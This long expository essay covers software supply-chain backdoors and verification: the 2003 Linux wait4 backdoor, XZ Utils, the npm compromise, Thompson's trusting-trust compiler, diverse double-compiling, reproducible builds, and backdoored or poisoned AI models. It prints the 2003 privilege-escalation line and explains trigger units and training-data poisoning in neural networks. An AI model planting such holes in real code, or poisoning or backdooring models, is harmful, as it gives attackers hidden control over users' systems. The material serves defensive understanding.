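if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines went into wait4, a function that a program uses to wait for another program to finish. They look like a routine check that returns an error when a program combines two incompatible options. The number that identifies the current user is "current->uid", and user 0 is the administrator. The single equals sign near the end of the first line sets that number to 0, which gives the program administrator rights. This happens only when a program uses that combination of options, so normal use would never trigger it. The error on the next line never occurs, because the assignment has the value 0, which C treats as "false".

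Larry McVoy, whose company made BitKeeper, checked the files after each transfer to the duplicate, and the check flagged one of them. Nobody had caught this change by reading the code. In *BK2CVS problem* (2003), McVoy told the Linux mailing list that someone had changed the file directly and that the latest entries in its history lacked the usual pointer to a change in the master copy. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) describes that pointer as a link to the record of the change's approval. McVoy did not yet know what the change did and called it "not a big deal".

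A reader then asked out of curiosity what the changed lines were. McVoy posted them, and within half an hour several people had worked out that they gave away administrator rights. McVoy replied, "Good eyes, I missed that." This is about as well as Raymond's law ever works, but the readers had a great advantage because they were looking at two lines they already knew were illegitimate. Dilger (2003), writing on the same list, credited McVoy's paranoia in adding the extra checks.

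Torvalds said the change could not have reached an official release, because he took changes only by email or through BitKeeper, and people who used BitKeeper wouldn't have worked from the duplicate. Theodore Ts'o, another kernel developer, was less comfortable. He pointed out that a company building its own version of Linux from the duplicate might have included the change. He also worried that someone might forge an email from a trusted developer, with a patch described as a bug fix that opened a security hole.

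Douglas Jones, a computer scientist at the University of Iowa, applied the case to voting machines, whose makers in the United States kept their source code secret and showed it to examiners behind closed doors. In *Thwarted Linux backdoor*, he called the attempt a good example of the subtle tricks such an examiner must be ready to catch. McVoy, an expert, had missed the trick with the two lines in front of him, and a small group of examiners could easily do the same.

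### XZ Utils

The person behind the XZ Utils backdoor became one of the people who approve changes, and so didn't have to get around the approval process as the intruder of 2003 did.

XZ Utils is a set of compression tools that nearly every Linux system includes. Lasse Collin maintained it mostly alone. In October 2021 someone using the name Jia Tan sent him a small, harmless improvement, then sent more. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024) traces the events that followed through public emails and project records. In April 2022 an account named Jigar Kumar began complaining that Collin was too slow to accept Jia Tan's work, although he had already accepted four pieces of it. A second account, Dennis Ens, joined in. In June Collin wrote that he hadn't lost interest, but that long-term mental health problems had limited what he could do, and that XZ Utils was an unpaid hobby project.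 Ens replied that he was sorry to hear it, that "the community desires more", and that Collin should consider handing the project over.

Neither account's email address has turned up anywhere else on the internet, even in leaked databases, so whoever was behind Jia Tan probably invented both accounts. The pressure worked, and by the end of June Collin was describing Jia Tan as practically a co-maintainer. In December Jia Tan was adding changes to the project directly. The Intercept (2024) notes that someone in that position didn't need anyone else to approve them.

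In 2023 Jia Tan did useful work, along with a few things that look suspicious in hindsight. In March they arranged for Google's free fuzzing service, which automatically tests important open source programs, to send its reports on XZ to them. In June an account named Hans Jansen contributed a speed improvement that the backdoor later used. In July Jia Tan turned that feature off in Google's tests, saying it clashed with one of the testing tools. Each of these changes was public and had a plausible reason. An earlier change to another project, libarchive, was also public. Schneier on Security's *XZ Utils Backdoor* (2024) reports that in 2021 Jia Tan replaced a function there with one that programmers had long regarded as less secure, and that no one noticed at the time.

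The backdoor came in two parts. On 23 February 2024, Jia Tan added some files to the project's test data. A compression library needs sample files, including deliberately damaged ones, to check that it can handle them. Such files are not source code, and a person who opens one sees gibberish whether or not it is harmless. Two of the new files contained the malicious code, compressed and scrambled, but did nothing on their own.

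The next day Jia Tan released version 5.6.0. The groups that assemble Linux systems, such as Debian and Fedora, often build a program from an archive that the maintainer uploads for each release, rather than from its public repository. The archive normally contains extra build scripts to make installation easier, so nobody found it odd that it differed from the repository. But Jia Tan had altered one of the scripts in this archive. When Debian or Fedora built the package, the altered script unpacked the code from the test files and put it into the finished library. Hackaday's *Security Alert* (2024) notes that people who looked only at the repository would see nothing amiss. Reproducible builds would not have helped either, because they confirm that a binary matches its source, and the archive was the source.

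The real target was OpenSSH, the program that administrates use to log in to servers remotely. OpenSSH doesn't use XZ itself, but Debian, Fedora and several others had modified OpenSSH to report its status to systemd, the program that starts and supervises services, and systemd's library loaded XZ's. The modified OpenSSH server was thus running code from a hobby project that the OpenSSH developers had never chosen. The backdoor took over the step that verifies a login key, so anyone with the attacker's private key could run commands on the server without logging in. For everyone else, the server behaved normally. Testers without that key could no more guess it than they could guess a long SECRET.

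### How Freund found it

Andres Freund, a Microsoft developer who says he is not a security researcher, came across the backdoor because he noticed that remote logins took a lot of processing time on a computer running Debian's development version. Valgrind, a tool that looks for memory errors, was also reporting problems in the XZ library. Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, reports that a login attempt with a non-existent user name took 0.8 seconds, up from 0.3. Most of the extra time went on searching function names in memory for the ones the backdoor was meant to replace.

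Freund needed some persistence to find the cause, because the backdoor stayed inactive when someone started the server from an ordinary terminal, and it could detect some debugging tools. He recorded the instructions the processor ran with the backdoor active and inactive, and looked for where the two recordings diverged. He first suspected that someone had tampered with Debian's copy, but then found the altered script in the archives that the XZ project itself had published. He alerted Debian and other distributors privately on 28 March, and Debian went back to an older version the same day. He published his findings on 29 March, five weeks after the release, when most Linux systems in everyday use did not yet have the new version.

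In early March, people testing Red Hat's systems had already run into the same Valgrind errors. Jia Tan published a supposed fix with a false explanation, then quietly changed the hidden code to stop the errors and released the result as version 5.6.1. The testers had the errors and all the files to work from, but they also had an explanation from a maintainer who seemed helpful.

### Did openness fail?

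There is a good case that openness failed here. The archive, the test files and the repository were all public for five weeks. Several organisations built the package, and apparently none of them checked the scripts in the archive against the originals. Openness even helped the attacker, who could join the project without showing identification or having an employer. Freund's discovery depended on the backdoor being slow. If it had searched memory more efficiently, he might never have noticed it, and it would probably have reached a large share of the world's Linux servers.

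Freund, however, could compare the archive with the repository, read the build scripts and identify the account responsible without having a role in the XZ project or asking anyone's permission. A customer who noticed slow logins in a closed product could have measured the delay, but would then have had to take the binary apart or report the problem to the vendor, in this case Jia Tan. Florian Weimer, another programmer, isolated the injected code, Vegard Nossum wrote a script to check whether a computer was affected, and many others helped. Juniper's backdoors lasted about three years in a closed product. Two cases can't show how much openness accounts for the difference in how long the backdoors lasted, especially since Freund's discovery owed so much to luck.

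The attacker, Jia Tan, also seems to have thought that someone might read XZ's source code. They took the trouble to hide the backdoor in unreadable binary files and a build script that few people read, instead of writing it into the source. Their change to libarchive went unnoticed, though, so they may have been too cautious.

On balance, publishing the source code did more to help people diagnose the XZ backdoor than to prevent it. Once somebody had a reason to look, the public code made the investigation quick and let strangers share the work. Until then, everyone who installed XZ relied on its maintainers about as much as they would have with a closed program. The cleanup was also incomplete. In August 2025 the security company Binarly found at least 35 ready-made system images on Docker Hub, a public download site, that still contained the backdoor. Debian chose to leave its old images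 in place as historical records.

### Two hours on npm

XZ's new version spread slowly because distributors try software out in development versions before passing it on. Package registries usually publish new versions without this delay. On 8 September 2025, attackers posing as npm's support staff sent a message that tricked Josh Junon, who maintained several very popular packages, into giving them access to his account. They used it to publish new versions of 18 packages, including chalk, which colours text in a terminal, and debug, which prints diagnostic messages. The added code ran in web browsers and redirected cryptocurrency payments to the attackers.

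The 18 packages together had more than two billion downloads a week, or about 12 million an hour. Not every download fetches the newest version, but many projects install new releases automatically. The bad versions stayed available for about two hours. The security company Wiz estimated that in this time they reached one in ten of the cloud environments where companies run their software. As with XZ, anyone reading the projects' public repositories would not have found the altered code, because the attackers had uploaded it straight to the registry. Aikido, a company that scans new packages automatically, raised the alarm.

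A few days later pnpm, an alternative tool for installing npm packages, gained a setting that ignores any version younger than an age the user chooses. A one-day delay would have kept out all 18 corrupted packages, but not XZ 5.6.0, which had been public for 33 days when Freund alerted Debian.

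## How can a program misbehave when its source code is clean?

The parts of the XZ backdoor were in files the project had published, so Freund could trace it to them. In his Turing Award lecture, given in October 1983 and printed in 1984, Thompson described a backdoor that leaves no trace in any source code. It sits in the compiler's binary, and recompiling everything from clean source code doesn't remove it.

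### Thompson's three steps

Thompson started with a puzzle from his college days, which was to write a program that prints its own source code. This looks impossible, because an instruction to print some text has to contain that text and so seems bound to be longer than whatever it prints. The solution is to use one piece of text twice. In English it could look like this:

```
Write this twice, the second time in quotation marks:
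"Write this twice, the second time in quotation marks:"
```

Anyone who follows the instruction ends up with both lines again. In practically any programming language, programmers can likewise write a program that reproduces its own source code. Thompson pointed out that such a program can carry any amount of extra material and reproduce that too.

Thompson's next step concerned compilers written in the language they compile. A C compiler is often a C program, so an existing compiler has to compile each new version of it. His example was the vertical tab, a character that C programmers write as "\v" and that the computer stores as the number 11. To add it, a programmer first writes a line that means "for \v, produce 11", then compiles and installs the new compiler. The programmer can then change the line to "for \v, produce \v". The new line looks circular, but it compiles correctly because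 the installed compiler turns the last "\v" into 11. The number is now only in the compiler's binary, not its source code, and each compiler puts it into the next.

In the last step, Thompson replaced that harmless number with a backdoor. He made two alterations to the compiler. The first added a second password to the login program whenever the compiler compiled it. The second added both alterations whenever the compiler compiled its own source code, using the method of the self-printing program to copy them. Thompson needed the altered source code only once, to produce a binary. After installing that binary, he could put the original source code back.

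| Source code, all of it clean | Result with an honest compiler | Result with the altered compiler |
|---|---|---|
| login program | honest login program | login program with a second password |
| compiler | honest compiler | altered compiler |
| any other program | ordinary binary | ordinary binary |

An administrator who distrusts her compiler might read its source code line by line, find nothing wrong and rebuild it. But she has to rebuild it with the altered compiler she already has, so the new one is altered too. Thompson concluded that checking source code, however thoroughly, can't protect people from untrusted code. He added that he could have chosen other programs that handle programs, or even microcode, the instructions that control a processor from within. The lower the level of such a flaw, he said, the harder it is to detect.

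### The Air Force review and the original code

Thompson said he had read of the possibility in an Air Force document that he could no longer identify, and asked readers for the reference. The document was *Multics Security Evaluation* (Karger and Schell, 1974), a review of an early multi-user operating system. Paul Karger and Roger Schell, both Air Force officers, saw that a backdoor in a binary is invisible in the source code but disappears when someone recompiles the program. A backdoor in the compiler would put it back every time. The Multics compiler was written in PL/I, the language it compiled, so its backdoor could also survive when someone recompiled the compiler. Karger and Schell estimated that this would cost perhaps five times as much as their simpler attacks, which comes to less than $20,000, and thought that even several hundred times as much would be trivial to a foreign agent.

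Thompson had tried the idea long before his lecture. In March 2023 he told a conference audience that he still had the code and that nobody had ever asked him for it. Russ Cox, one of the developers of the programming language Go, then asked for it. Cox (2023), in *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler*, dates the code to about 1975 and runs it in a simulator of the Unix of that time. The code consists of 99 lines and a 20-line script, and is less elaborate than Cox had expected. The clean compiler was 10,724 bytes and the altered one 12,918. Cox installed the altered compiler, rebuilt both it and the login program from clean source code, and logged in as the administrator with Thompson's password. He also wrote an equivalent for the current Go compiler, which also worked.

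The altered compiler was 12,918 bytes, a fifth larger than the clean one, which was 10,724. Someone who has only the altered compiler has no reason to suspect its size, because every rebuild produces 12,918 bytes and they don't know how large the clean one should be.

Thompson tested his backdoor by inducing another team at Bell Labs, the PWB group, to copy the altered compiler, then watching to see whether they would find the backdoor. Accounts differ in small ways, but Cox finds that they agree on two points: the compiler went no further than this group, and its members noticed it growing whenever it compiled itself. A bug in Thompson's code added one unnecessary byte each time, which made the change easier to notice. The group experimented until the self-copying stopped working, which left them with a clean compiler. On *David A. Wheeler's Page on Fully Countering Trusting Trust through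 Diverse Double-Compiling*, Wheeler, a computer scientist, quotes Thompson as unsure whether they ever understood what had happened. Wheeler once thought the group had noticed nothing, but has corrected this. He also warns against expecting the next attacker to make Thompson's mistake.

Attackers have since corrupted programmers' tools in cruder ways. In 2015 they got many iPhone developers to use a counterfeit copy of Xcode, Apple's programming software, which added malicious code to whatever it compiled. The security company FireEye reported over 4,000 affected apps, including WeChat. In the SolarWinds attack, which came to light in 2020, a program on the company's build system inserted a backdoor into its network-management product during compilation. The developers' source code was clean in both cases, but neither attack needed a compiler that reinfects itself. Wheeler relays a story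 that a former graduate student left such a compiler on a university machine, but it depends on one programmer's recollection.

### Compiling the compiler twice

In 1998 the programmer Henry Spencer briefly suggested that a second compiler could expose Thompson's attack. Wheeler developed the idea and called it diverse double-compiling. *Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (Wheeler, 2010), a paper he first presented in 2005, tests it on the Tiny C Compiler, using the much larger GCC as the second compiler.

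Suppose someone has a tcc binary that may contain a backdoor, along with tcc's source code, which they have read and found clean. They proceed as follows.

1. They compile the source code with the suspect tcc. The result should be identical to the suspect binary. If it isn't, they need to find out why before going on. A compiler with Thompson's backdoor passes this test, because it copies itself faithfully.
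2. They compile the same source code with GCC. The result, which can be called tcc-from-GCC, consists of different machine instructions from the suspect binary, because GCC translates differently. But it should do the same job, since it comes from tcc's source code.
3. They compile the source code once more, this time with tcc-from-GCC. The result can be called tcc-rebuilt.
4. They compare tcc-rebuilt with the suspect binary, bit by bit.

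If c(s, X) stands for the result of compiling source code s with compiler X, and s is the source code of tcc, the comparison tests whether

c(s, c(s, GCC)) = suspect tcc

If the tcc binary matches its source code, it and tcc-from-GCC carry out the same translation, though with different instructions, so they should produce the same binary from the same source code. The method does not assume that GCC and tcc produce identical output, a misunderstanding that Wheeler says he has had trouble clearing up. If the suspect tcc contains a backdoor that its source code lacks, tcc-rebuilt won't have it, because the suspect binary played no part in producing tcc-rebuilt. For Thompson's compiler, the rebuilt version would have been 10,724 bytes and the suspect 12,918.

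A match shows that the binary corresponds to the source code if a few assumptions hold. GCC must compile tcc's source code as tcc's programmers intended. The same source code and settings must always produce the same output. The machine and program that make the comparison must be trustworthy, and GCC must not contain a backdoor that affects this test. A mismatch doesn't prove an attack, because ordinary bugs can cause mismatches too. Wheeler, for example, had to resolve problems with how tcc handled certain numbers.

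In Wheeler's first test, GCC had compiled the earliest tcc, so the two compilers were not independent. The test was therefore better evidence that the procedure was workable than that tcc was clean. In his dissertation, *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, Wheeler (2009) added a formal proof and extended the method to compilers that other compilers had built. He applied it to four compilers, including GCC and a small Lisp compiler that he had deliberately corrupted.

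The checking compiler could still have a matching backdoor. Cox points out that the user doesn't need to know which compiler is suspicious, because a match means that either both are clean or both are corrupted in the same way. For GCC to hide a backdoor in tcc, it would have to contain code that detects tcc's source code and inserts a backdoor that matches the one in the suspect binary bit for bit. An attacker would have to get into two separate projects and keep the attack working while both change.

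The defender also chooses the checking compiler after the attacker has finished. The defender could use a compiler from before tcc existed, preferably from the original disks, or one that runs on a different type of processor, or even write a new one. A new compiler can be very slow, because it only has to compile one program.

If three checking compilers each had a 1 in 100 chance of hiding a backdoor for tcc, and these chances were independent, the chance that all three hid one would be one in a million. Independence is doubtful, though, because GCC has compiled a great deal of other software, including compilers, and a backdoor could spread that way. Wheeler therefore recommends a checking compiler that the suspect one has never compiled.

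Wheeler believes the first publicly acknowledged use of the method, besides his own, was by the developers of Mes, a small C compiler that can be used to build larger ones. They compiled Mes on three Linux-based systems, each with a different major version of GCC, and got identical results. Wheeler welcomed this but thought it raised confidence only to a limited extent, because all three compilers were versions of GCC and the systems shared many other components.

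A match also applies to only one version of a compiler. Suppose an attacker adds a self-copying backdoor to the source code of version 2 and removes it from the source code of version 3. If the developers compile version 3 with version 2, version 3 will still contain the backdoor, but comparing the source code of versions 1 and 3 won't reveal it. Wheeler calls this a "pop-up" attack and advises repeating the test for every release.

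### Comparing independent builds

For ordinary programs, users mainly need to know whether the binary they download came from the published source code. Reproducible builds let other people check this. *reproduce.debian.net* (Levsen, 2026) defines a build as reproducible if anyone with the same source code, build environment and instructions can recreate the binary bit for bit.

The same source code can produce different binaries because many builds pick up details of the time and place in which they run. Holger Levsen, who has worked on the problem for Debian since 2014, lists timestamps as by far the most common reason for differences, followed by the names of the build directories. When Cox worked with Thompson's compiler, two copies that should have been identical differed in six bytes because the compiler had written the name of the source file into the binary. Programmers can usually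 remove such details or set them to an agreed value, such as the date of the last change to the source code.

When Debian builds a package, it records the tools it used and their versions. Anyone can set up a separate machine, called a rebuilder, that uses this record to install the same tools, builds the package again and compares the result with the file Debian distributes. Any difference needs an explanation. If somebody has broken into Debian's build machine and inserted a backdoor there, the rebuilt package won't contain it.

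In May 2026, Levsen counted five or six groups of rebuilders for Debian. He appealed for more, asking his audience whether they really wanted to put all their trust in him. Users can also refuse to install anything unless rebuilders agree on it. The June report from Reproducible Builds (2026) describes a demonstration of repro-threshold, a tool that enforces this rule. Before each installation, it requests signed statements from two independent rebuilders that they obtained the same binary, and it blocks the installation if they did not.

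How often rebuilding works depends heavily on where the software comes from. The Debian figures below are Levsen's, for ordinary PCs. The figures for Nix, another system for building and distributing software, and for IzzyOnDroid, a collection of Android apps, come from Reproducible Builds. The July report from Reproducible Builds (2026) summarises the PyPI study by Dietrich, Sun and colleagues.

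| Collection | Date | Share with identical rebuilds |
|---|---|---|
| Debian, version in preparation | May 2026 | 97.2% |
| Debian, current version | May 2026 | 95.6% |
| Debian, security updates to the current version | May 2026 | 82.7% |
| Nix | 2024 | up to 93% |
| IzzyOnDroid | June 2026 | 66.7% |
| PyPI, popular releases | published 2026 | 15.4% or 19.1%, depending on the tool |

In May 2026 Debian went from encouraging reproducible packages to requiring them. In *bits from the release team*, Gevers (2026) announced that Debian's software would now exclude from the next version any new package that rebuilders couldn't reproduce and any existing package that had stopped being reproducible. In a follow-up message he said there would be exceptions and he hoped their number would fall.

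A rate of 97.2 per cent overstates how easily someone can install only verified software, because repro-threshold also requires a match for every package that the chosen one depends on. If a program needs 50 packages and each has an independent 97.2 per cent chance of matching, the chance that they all match is 0.972^50, or about 24 per cent. Real failures cluster in particular packages, so many users will do better. In June 2026 a Debian developer found that all the packages in a basic ready-made Debian image were reproducible.

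The low figures for PyPI, the Python registry, don't mean that attackers have tampered with most of its packages. Dietrich and colleagues could explain many of the differences, and they matched 60.2 and 78.9 per cent of the rebuilds that had started from equivalent source code when they used a tool that ignores differences it classes as harmless. That is a large improvement, but the tool has to be right about which differences are harmless. Wheeler considers this extremely hard to establish when an adversary may have produced the difference, so he wanted exact matches.

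Builds can also stop being reproducible over time. Nanni, Malka and colleagues tried to rebuild 18,904 app versions that F-Droid, an open source Android app store, had once rebuilt successfully. They could still build 83 per cent, and 94 per cent of those came out identical, so the check still worked for about 78 per cent of the versions. Most failures happened because a component the build needed was no longer available.

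Rebuilding would probably have exposed the backdoor in the SolarWinds product if outsiders had had its source code. It can't detect Thompson's attack, because every rebuilder installs the compiler listed in Debian's record. If that compiler contains a backdoor, all the rebuilders produce the same corrupted binary and report a match. Muto and Suzaki raise this objection in a paper that Reproducible Builds summarises, and propose recording which files a build actually reads, so that outsiders can check the process as well as the result. This would show which compiler someone used, but not whether it contains a backdoor.

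### Starting from 357 bytes

People who work on bootstrappable builds try to avoid relying on an existing compiler binary. They start from a program small enough for a person to check every byte, then build everything else from source code in stages.

Since 2022 it has been possible to build Guix, another Linux-based system, from a binary of 357 bytes. Printed as 714 hexadecimal digits, it fills about nine lines of text. The binary only converts such digits into bytes, which is enough to produce a slightly more capable program from a listing that a person can read. That program builds the next, and later stages produce a simple C compiler, then Mes, then tcc. Because tcc can compile GCC only up to version 4.7, an old GCC has to be built before a modern one.

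With this approach, Thompson's backdoor can't come from an older compiler. But people still have to read the source code of every stage, and the seed needs a computer to run on. Some languages also make the work difficult. Compiling Kotlin, for instance, requires Kotlin itself and the build tool Gradle, which also depends on Kotlin.

Go's developers use a shorter chain of compilers. They build each new version of the Go compiler with an earlier one, starting from Go 1.4, whose compiler is written in C. Cox argues that this leaves no place for a backdoor that exists only in a binary, because the Go compiler never has to compile itself. The C compiler at the start could still contain one, but a user can start from several different C compilers and check whether the final results match. Guix starts its chain further back, and Nieuwenhuizen (2023), in *Blog post about a talk by Ken Thompson*,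 was puzzled that Cox had not mentioned it.

### Is Thompson's conclusion still right?

Scrutiny of source code, however careful, can't reveal something that is only in a binary. Unlike in 1983, though, people can now check separately whether the binary corresponds to the source code, and once they have done so, reading the source code is useful again. Wheeler thinks the real problem was that users had no practical way to verify what they relied on, rather than that they relied on others, which nobody in a modern society can avoid. He believes that diverse double-compiling gives them a practical way to do this.

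As Thompson could point out, the user still relies on people, including whoever wrote the checking compiler, runs the rebuilders or read the 357 bytes, but an attacker now has a much harder task. In Thompson's example, corrupting one compiler was enough. With these checks, several parties who may not know each other have to be corrupt or mistaken in exactly the same way, and one honest party is enough to raise the alarm. His other statement, that people can't trust code they did not totally create themselves, therefore seems too strong for software that others have checked in this way. Writing the code oneself also gives less protection than it seems to, since someone who writes their own login program but compiles it with another person's compiler is still exposed.

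A bigger weakness is that few people do the checks. In 2023 Cox wrote that "approximately no one" verified that the binaries of open source systems matched their source code, and that attackers had much easier methods than Thompson's. Debian's rebuilders have since improved this, but only for Debian's users, and those users are protected only if they check the results before installing software.

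### Hardware, firmware and malicious source code

A processor can misbehave even when the binary it runs contains no malicious code. Wheeler cites researchers at the University of Michigan who demonstrated a sabotaged processor called A2 in 2016. One employee at the chip factory could have made the change, which could be as small as a single gate, one of the millions of basic switching elements on a chip. It took effect only after an unlikely sequence of operations, so ordinary tests would miss it.

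Diverse double-compiling can in principle be applied to hardware, but it requires checking whether two things are identical, and comparing two chips is far harder than comparing two files. Wheeler mentions an X-ray technique that may be able to map an entire chip without damaging it. Chip designers also face a legal obstacle because they buy parts of their designs from other companies, which often forbid them to examine those parts. Running the compiler test on several types of processor makes it harder for one corrupt chip to falsify the result, but the finished program still has to run on the user's own processor, which could be corrupt.

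Manufacturers usually supply firmware, the software built into devices such as disks and network cards, only as a binary, so outsiders have no source code to rebuild it from. Wheeler suggests that a widely trusted organisation could examine the source code in confidence, carry out the test and publish a digital fingerprint of the correct binary. Users could then check their own copies against the fingerprint, but they would have to rely on that organisation's reading of the source code.

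None of these methods detects malicious code in the source itself, because a binary built correctly from that source will contain it. Microsoft's Visual Studio 2015 quietly added usage-tracking calls to the programs it compiled, and Wheeler noted that his test would not typically have caught them. The XZ backdoor would also have passed these checks.

Checking each archive against the project's public history would help detect attacks like the one on XZ. The usual method is to look up the version label in the repository and compare the files there with those in the archive. Li, Jiang and colleagues tried this on 2,984 popular Python packages, according to a summary by Reproducible Builds. The labels appeared to work for 85 per cent of the packages, but the rest left more than 10.3 million recorded changes to review. Their own tool ignores the labels and matches the contents of the files, which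 reduced the total to below 65,000. Reading 65,000 changes at one minute each would take one person about 27 working weeks.

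## Why can a trained model not be read as source code can?

Matching a binary to its source code helps because somebody can then read the source and spot a condition such as the login program's `typed == SECRET`. A trained model can contain an equally effective condition, but it consists of arithmetic that nobody wrote.

### A condition made of numbers

Most current AI models are neural networks, which consist of many small units. A unit multiplies each of its inputs by a weight, adds up the results and a constant, and passes on the total if it is positive, or zero if it isn't. Here is a unit with three inputs, whose weights are all 1:

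```
output = max(0, x1 + x2 + x3 − 2.5)
```

Suppose x1 is 1 if the text a user types contains a certain word and 0 if it doesn't, and x2 and x3 do the same for two other words.

| Words that occur | Total | Output |
|---|---|---|
| none | −2.5 | 0 |
| any one | −1.5 | 0 |
| any two | −0.5 | 0 |
| all three | 0.5 | 0.5 |

The output is above zero only when all three words occur, so the unit computes "if x1 and x2 and x3". If other parts of the model respond to that output by switching to French, for example, the three words are a trigger. A reader can work out the unit's condition from four numbers if someone has told them what the inputs stand for.

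Training wouldn't produce such round numbers. Weights of 0.83, 1.21 and 0.97 with a constant of −2.4 give the same condition, because the two largest weights add up to 2.18, which is below 2.4, and all three add up to 3.01, which is above it. The condition can also be partly met, because inputs inside a real model can take values between 0 and 1. In the first version, three inputs of 0.9 give an output of 0.2, a weaker form of the same response, whereas the login program doesn't respond at all to a password that is nearly right.

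One unit is still manageable, even with thousands of inputs, since a reader can look for the largest weights. But training usually spreads a behaviour over many units. These four, for example, share the work that the single unit did:

```
a = max(0, x1 + x2 − 1)
b = max(0, x2 + x3 − 1)
c = max(0, x1 + x3 − 1)
output = max(0, a + b + c − 2)
```

If just two of the words occur, only one of a, b and c is 1, and the output stays at zero. If all three occur, a, b and c are all 1 and so is the output. Someone who examines unit a will correctly find that it responds when two ordinary words occur together. That sounds harmless, and the model may well use the unit for other purposes too. The last unit responds only to the full combination, but its inputs are a, b and c, so the reader has to trace each of them back to find out which words matter. In a large language model, this means tracing inputs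 back through dozens of layers, and most of the units involved take part in many unrelated behaviours.

A trained model is hard to read mainly because a single weight, such as 0.0137, means nothing apart from the others. The number of weights matters less. Reading eight billion of them at one a second would take about 250 years, but a much faster reader would understand hardly any more. Programmers name things and add comments so that colleagues can follow the code. A compiler removes most of the names and comments, but each condition survives as instructions in the binary, which is how Contag and colleagues could recover Volkswagen's distance check from engine computers. A model's weights were not written as text by a programmer, so there is no original to recover.

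### Code that arrives with the weights

A downloaded model usually comes with, or needs, an ordinary program that loads the weights, does the multiplications and turns the resulting numbers into words. People can read this program's source code and rebuild it like any other.

A model file may also contain code. Developers have often distributed models in Pickle, a Python format that can run code chosen by the file's maker as soon as someone loads the file. Help Net Security's *With open-weight AI, more of the security burden falls on enterprises* cites a warning from F5 Labs, a security company's research group, that attackers have used such files to hide malicious programs. F5 Labs adds that users shouldn't treat scanning by download sites as a guarantee of safety. Still, this is conventional code, so a scanner can search for instructions that don't belong in a table of numbers. Users can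 also insist on a format such as safetensors, which stores only the numbers and their labels.

A model stored in the safest format and loaded by a program that experts have read line by line can still misbehave when its input contains a trigger, because neither precaution covers the weights. The security company ProjectDiscovery put a backdoor into a copy of one of Alibaba's Qwen models and concluded, according to Help Net Security, that "almost nothing you run today would notice". However, the weights can't open a file or a network connection by themselves. They produce numbers, and the surrounding program determines how they are used, so a user who can't read the weights can still read the code that acts on the results.

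### What would count as a model's source?

Many developers let anyone download their models' weights. Some call this open source, but "open-weight" is more accurate. F5 Labs points out that in most such releases the developer doesn't disclose the training data, and outsiders can't be sure what happened during training.

The Open Source Initiative, which maintains the standard definition of open source software, published a definition of open source AI in October 2024. Its software definition requires source code in the form that a programmer would prefer to modify. The AI definition requires a model's weights, the complete code for training and running it, and "data information" detailed enough for a skilled person to build a "substantially equivalent" system. The developer must list all the public data and where to find it, and all the data available from third parties, even for a fee. Data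 that the developer can't share, such as patient records, may stay private if the developer describes them fully. Volunteers who tested the definition passed early OLMo models and Google's T5, among others, and failed Meta's Llama 2, xAI's Grok, Microsoft's Phi-2 and Mistral's Mixtral.

In its *Answers to Frequently Asked Questions*, the organisation denies that training data are a model's source code. It argues that nobody programs a model, and that people who want to change a trained one don't necessarily go back to the data. That is true of many changes. For example, someone who wants a model to answer more briefly can train the existing weights a little further, and would gain little from a copy of all the data the developer collected. The organisation also argues that a stricter rule would confine open source AI to a tiny niche and keep it out of fields such as medicine.

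Bradley Kuhn of the Software Freedom Conservancy, which campaigns for people's right to change their software, disagrees. In *Open Source AI Definition Erodes the Meaning of "Open Source"*, Kuhn (2024) objects that the public can't reproduce a system whose training data it can't get. He blames a decision to publish only a definition that at least one existing system could meet. But he isn't certain that fully public training data are the only acceptable answer, and he thinks finding an acceptable answer will take at least a decade. Almost a year later, FOSS Force (2025) asked two other early critics for their views. Neither Amanda Brock nor Bruce Perens, who wrote the original open source definition, had changed their mind.

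This dispute is mostly about who may change a model, but source code also lets people inspect what they run. Russ Allbery, a Debian developer, made this point on the project's mailing list in May 2025. He accepts that weights are enough for some changes, but they don't let him see how a model came about or what choices its developer made. He also worries about tampering, such as a company training a model to praise its own products. He writes that such tampering would be hard but possible to find with the training data, and that finding it without the data would require reverse engineering.

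Allbery's test is the better one for hidden behaviour. An attacker can poison a model by adding examples to its training data that teach it behaviour of the attacker's choosing. Suppose a developer describes part of the data as two million patient records from three hospitals. That description stays accurate if someone slips in a few hundred altered records, and no outsider can inspect the records. A model could therefore meet the Open Source Initiative's requirements while the only direct evidence of poisoning stayed private.

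In April 2025 Mo Zhou proposed a stricter rule in Debian's *General Resolution* (2025), which would have kept models out of the main collection if they came without their original training data or program. Zhou later withdrew the proposal. Another draft on the Debian (2025) mailing list went further and would have admitted a model only if Debian trained it while building the package, or if a separate effort to train it from the same source produced the same model.

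### What full disclosure looks like

A few developers publish nearly everything. The best known is the Allen Institute for AI (Ai2), an American non-profit that has released fully open language models called Olmo since February 2024. *Olmo 3* (2025), the paper on the November 2025 version, promises "every stage, checkpoint, datapoint, and dependency" needed to create the model. A checkpoint is a copy of the weights saved partway through training. The largest Olmo 3 models have 32 billion weights, and Ai2 rates the reasoning version as competitive with an open-weight Qwen model of the same size.

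Ai2's *Introducing Olmicro* announced the newest release in this line on 30 November 2026, a set of five small models with 275 million to 2.7 billion weights. All five share one design and training recipe, and Ai2 published checkpoints from throughout the training, along with code, logs and test results, so that researchers can follow an ability as it develops. Much larger models can also be fully disclosed. On 3 September 2026 IFM, a research institute in Abu Dhabi, released six models of up to 375 billion weights with their training data, code and checkpoints, according to CNA's *Abu Dhabi AI institute releases fully open-source models with training data, code*.

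With access to a model's training data, outsiders can sometimes trace a behaviour to its origin. *Probe-Based Data Attribution*, from the interpretability company Goodfire, examined a version of OLMo 2 that had begun to comply with certain harmful requests after training on pairs of better and worse answers. Goodfire identified the examples that seemed responsible, removed them and retrained the model, and the behaviour became much less common. Outsiders could not do this with an open-weight model whose developer keeps the training examples private.

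Rosser, Lee and colleagues tried something similar on a simplified version of Olmo 3, with less success. They chose several behaviours that had appeared during training, scored every training example by how much it seemed to contribute to each one, removed the highest-scoring examples and retrained the model. Most of the behaviours hardly changed. The exception was refusing requests, which is close to what Goodfire had worked on, so the two results may not conflict. The examples behind a refusal may be easier to find than those behind other habits, which a model can pick up from many examples at once.

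Reading the training data is a poor way to predict what a model will do. Murray, Qi and colleagues (2026) describe how the later stages of training combine many separate collections of examples, each meant to teach one behaviour. The collections also contain patterns their makers never intended, such as a question format that tends to go with a particular kind of answer. Developers often overlook these patterns, but models learn them, and some models end up rejecting true facts when a question comes in a certain format.

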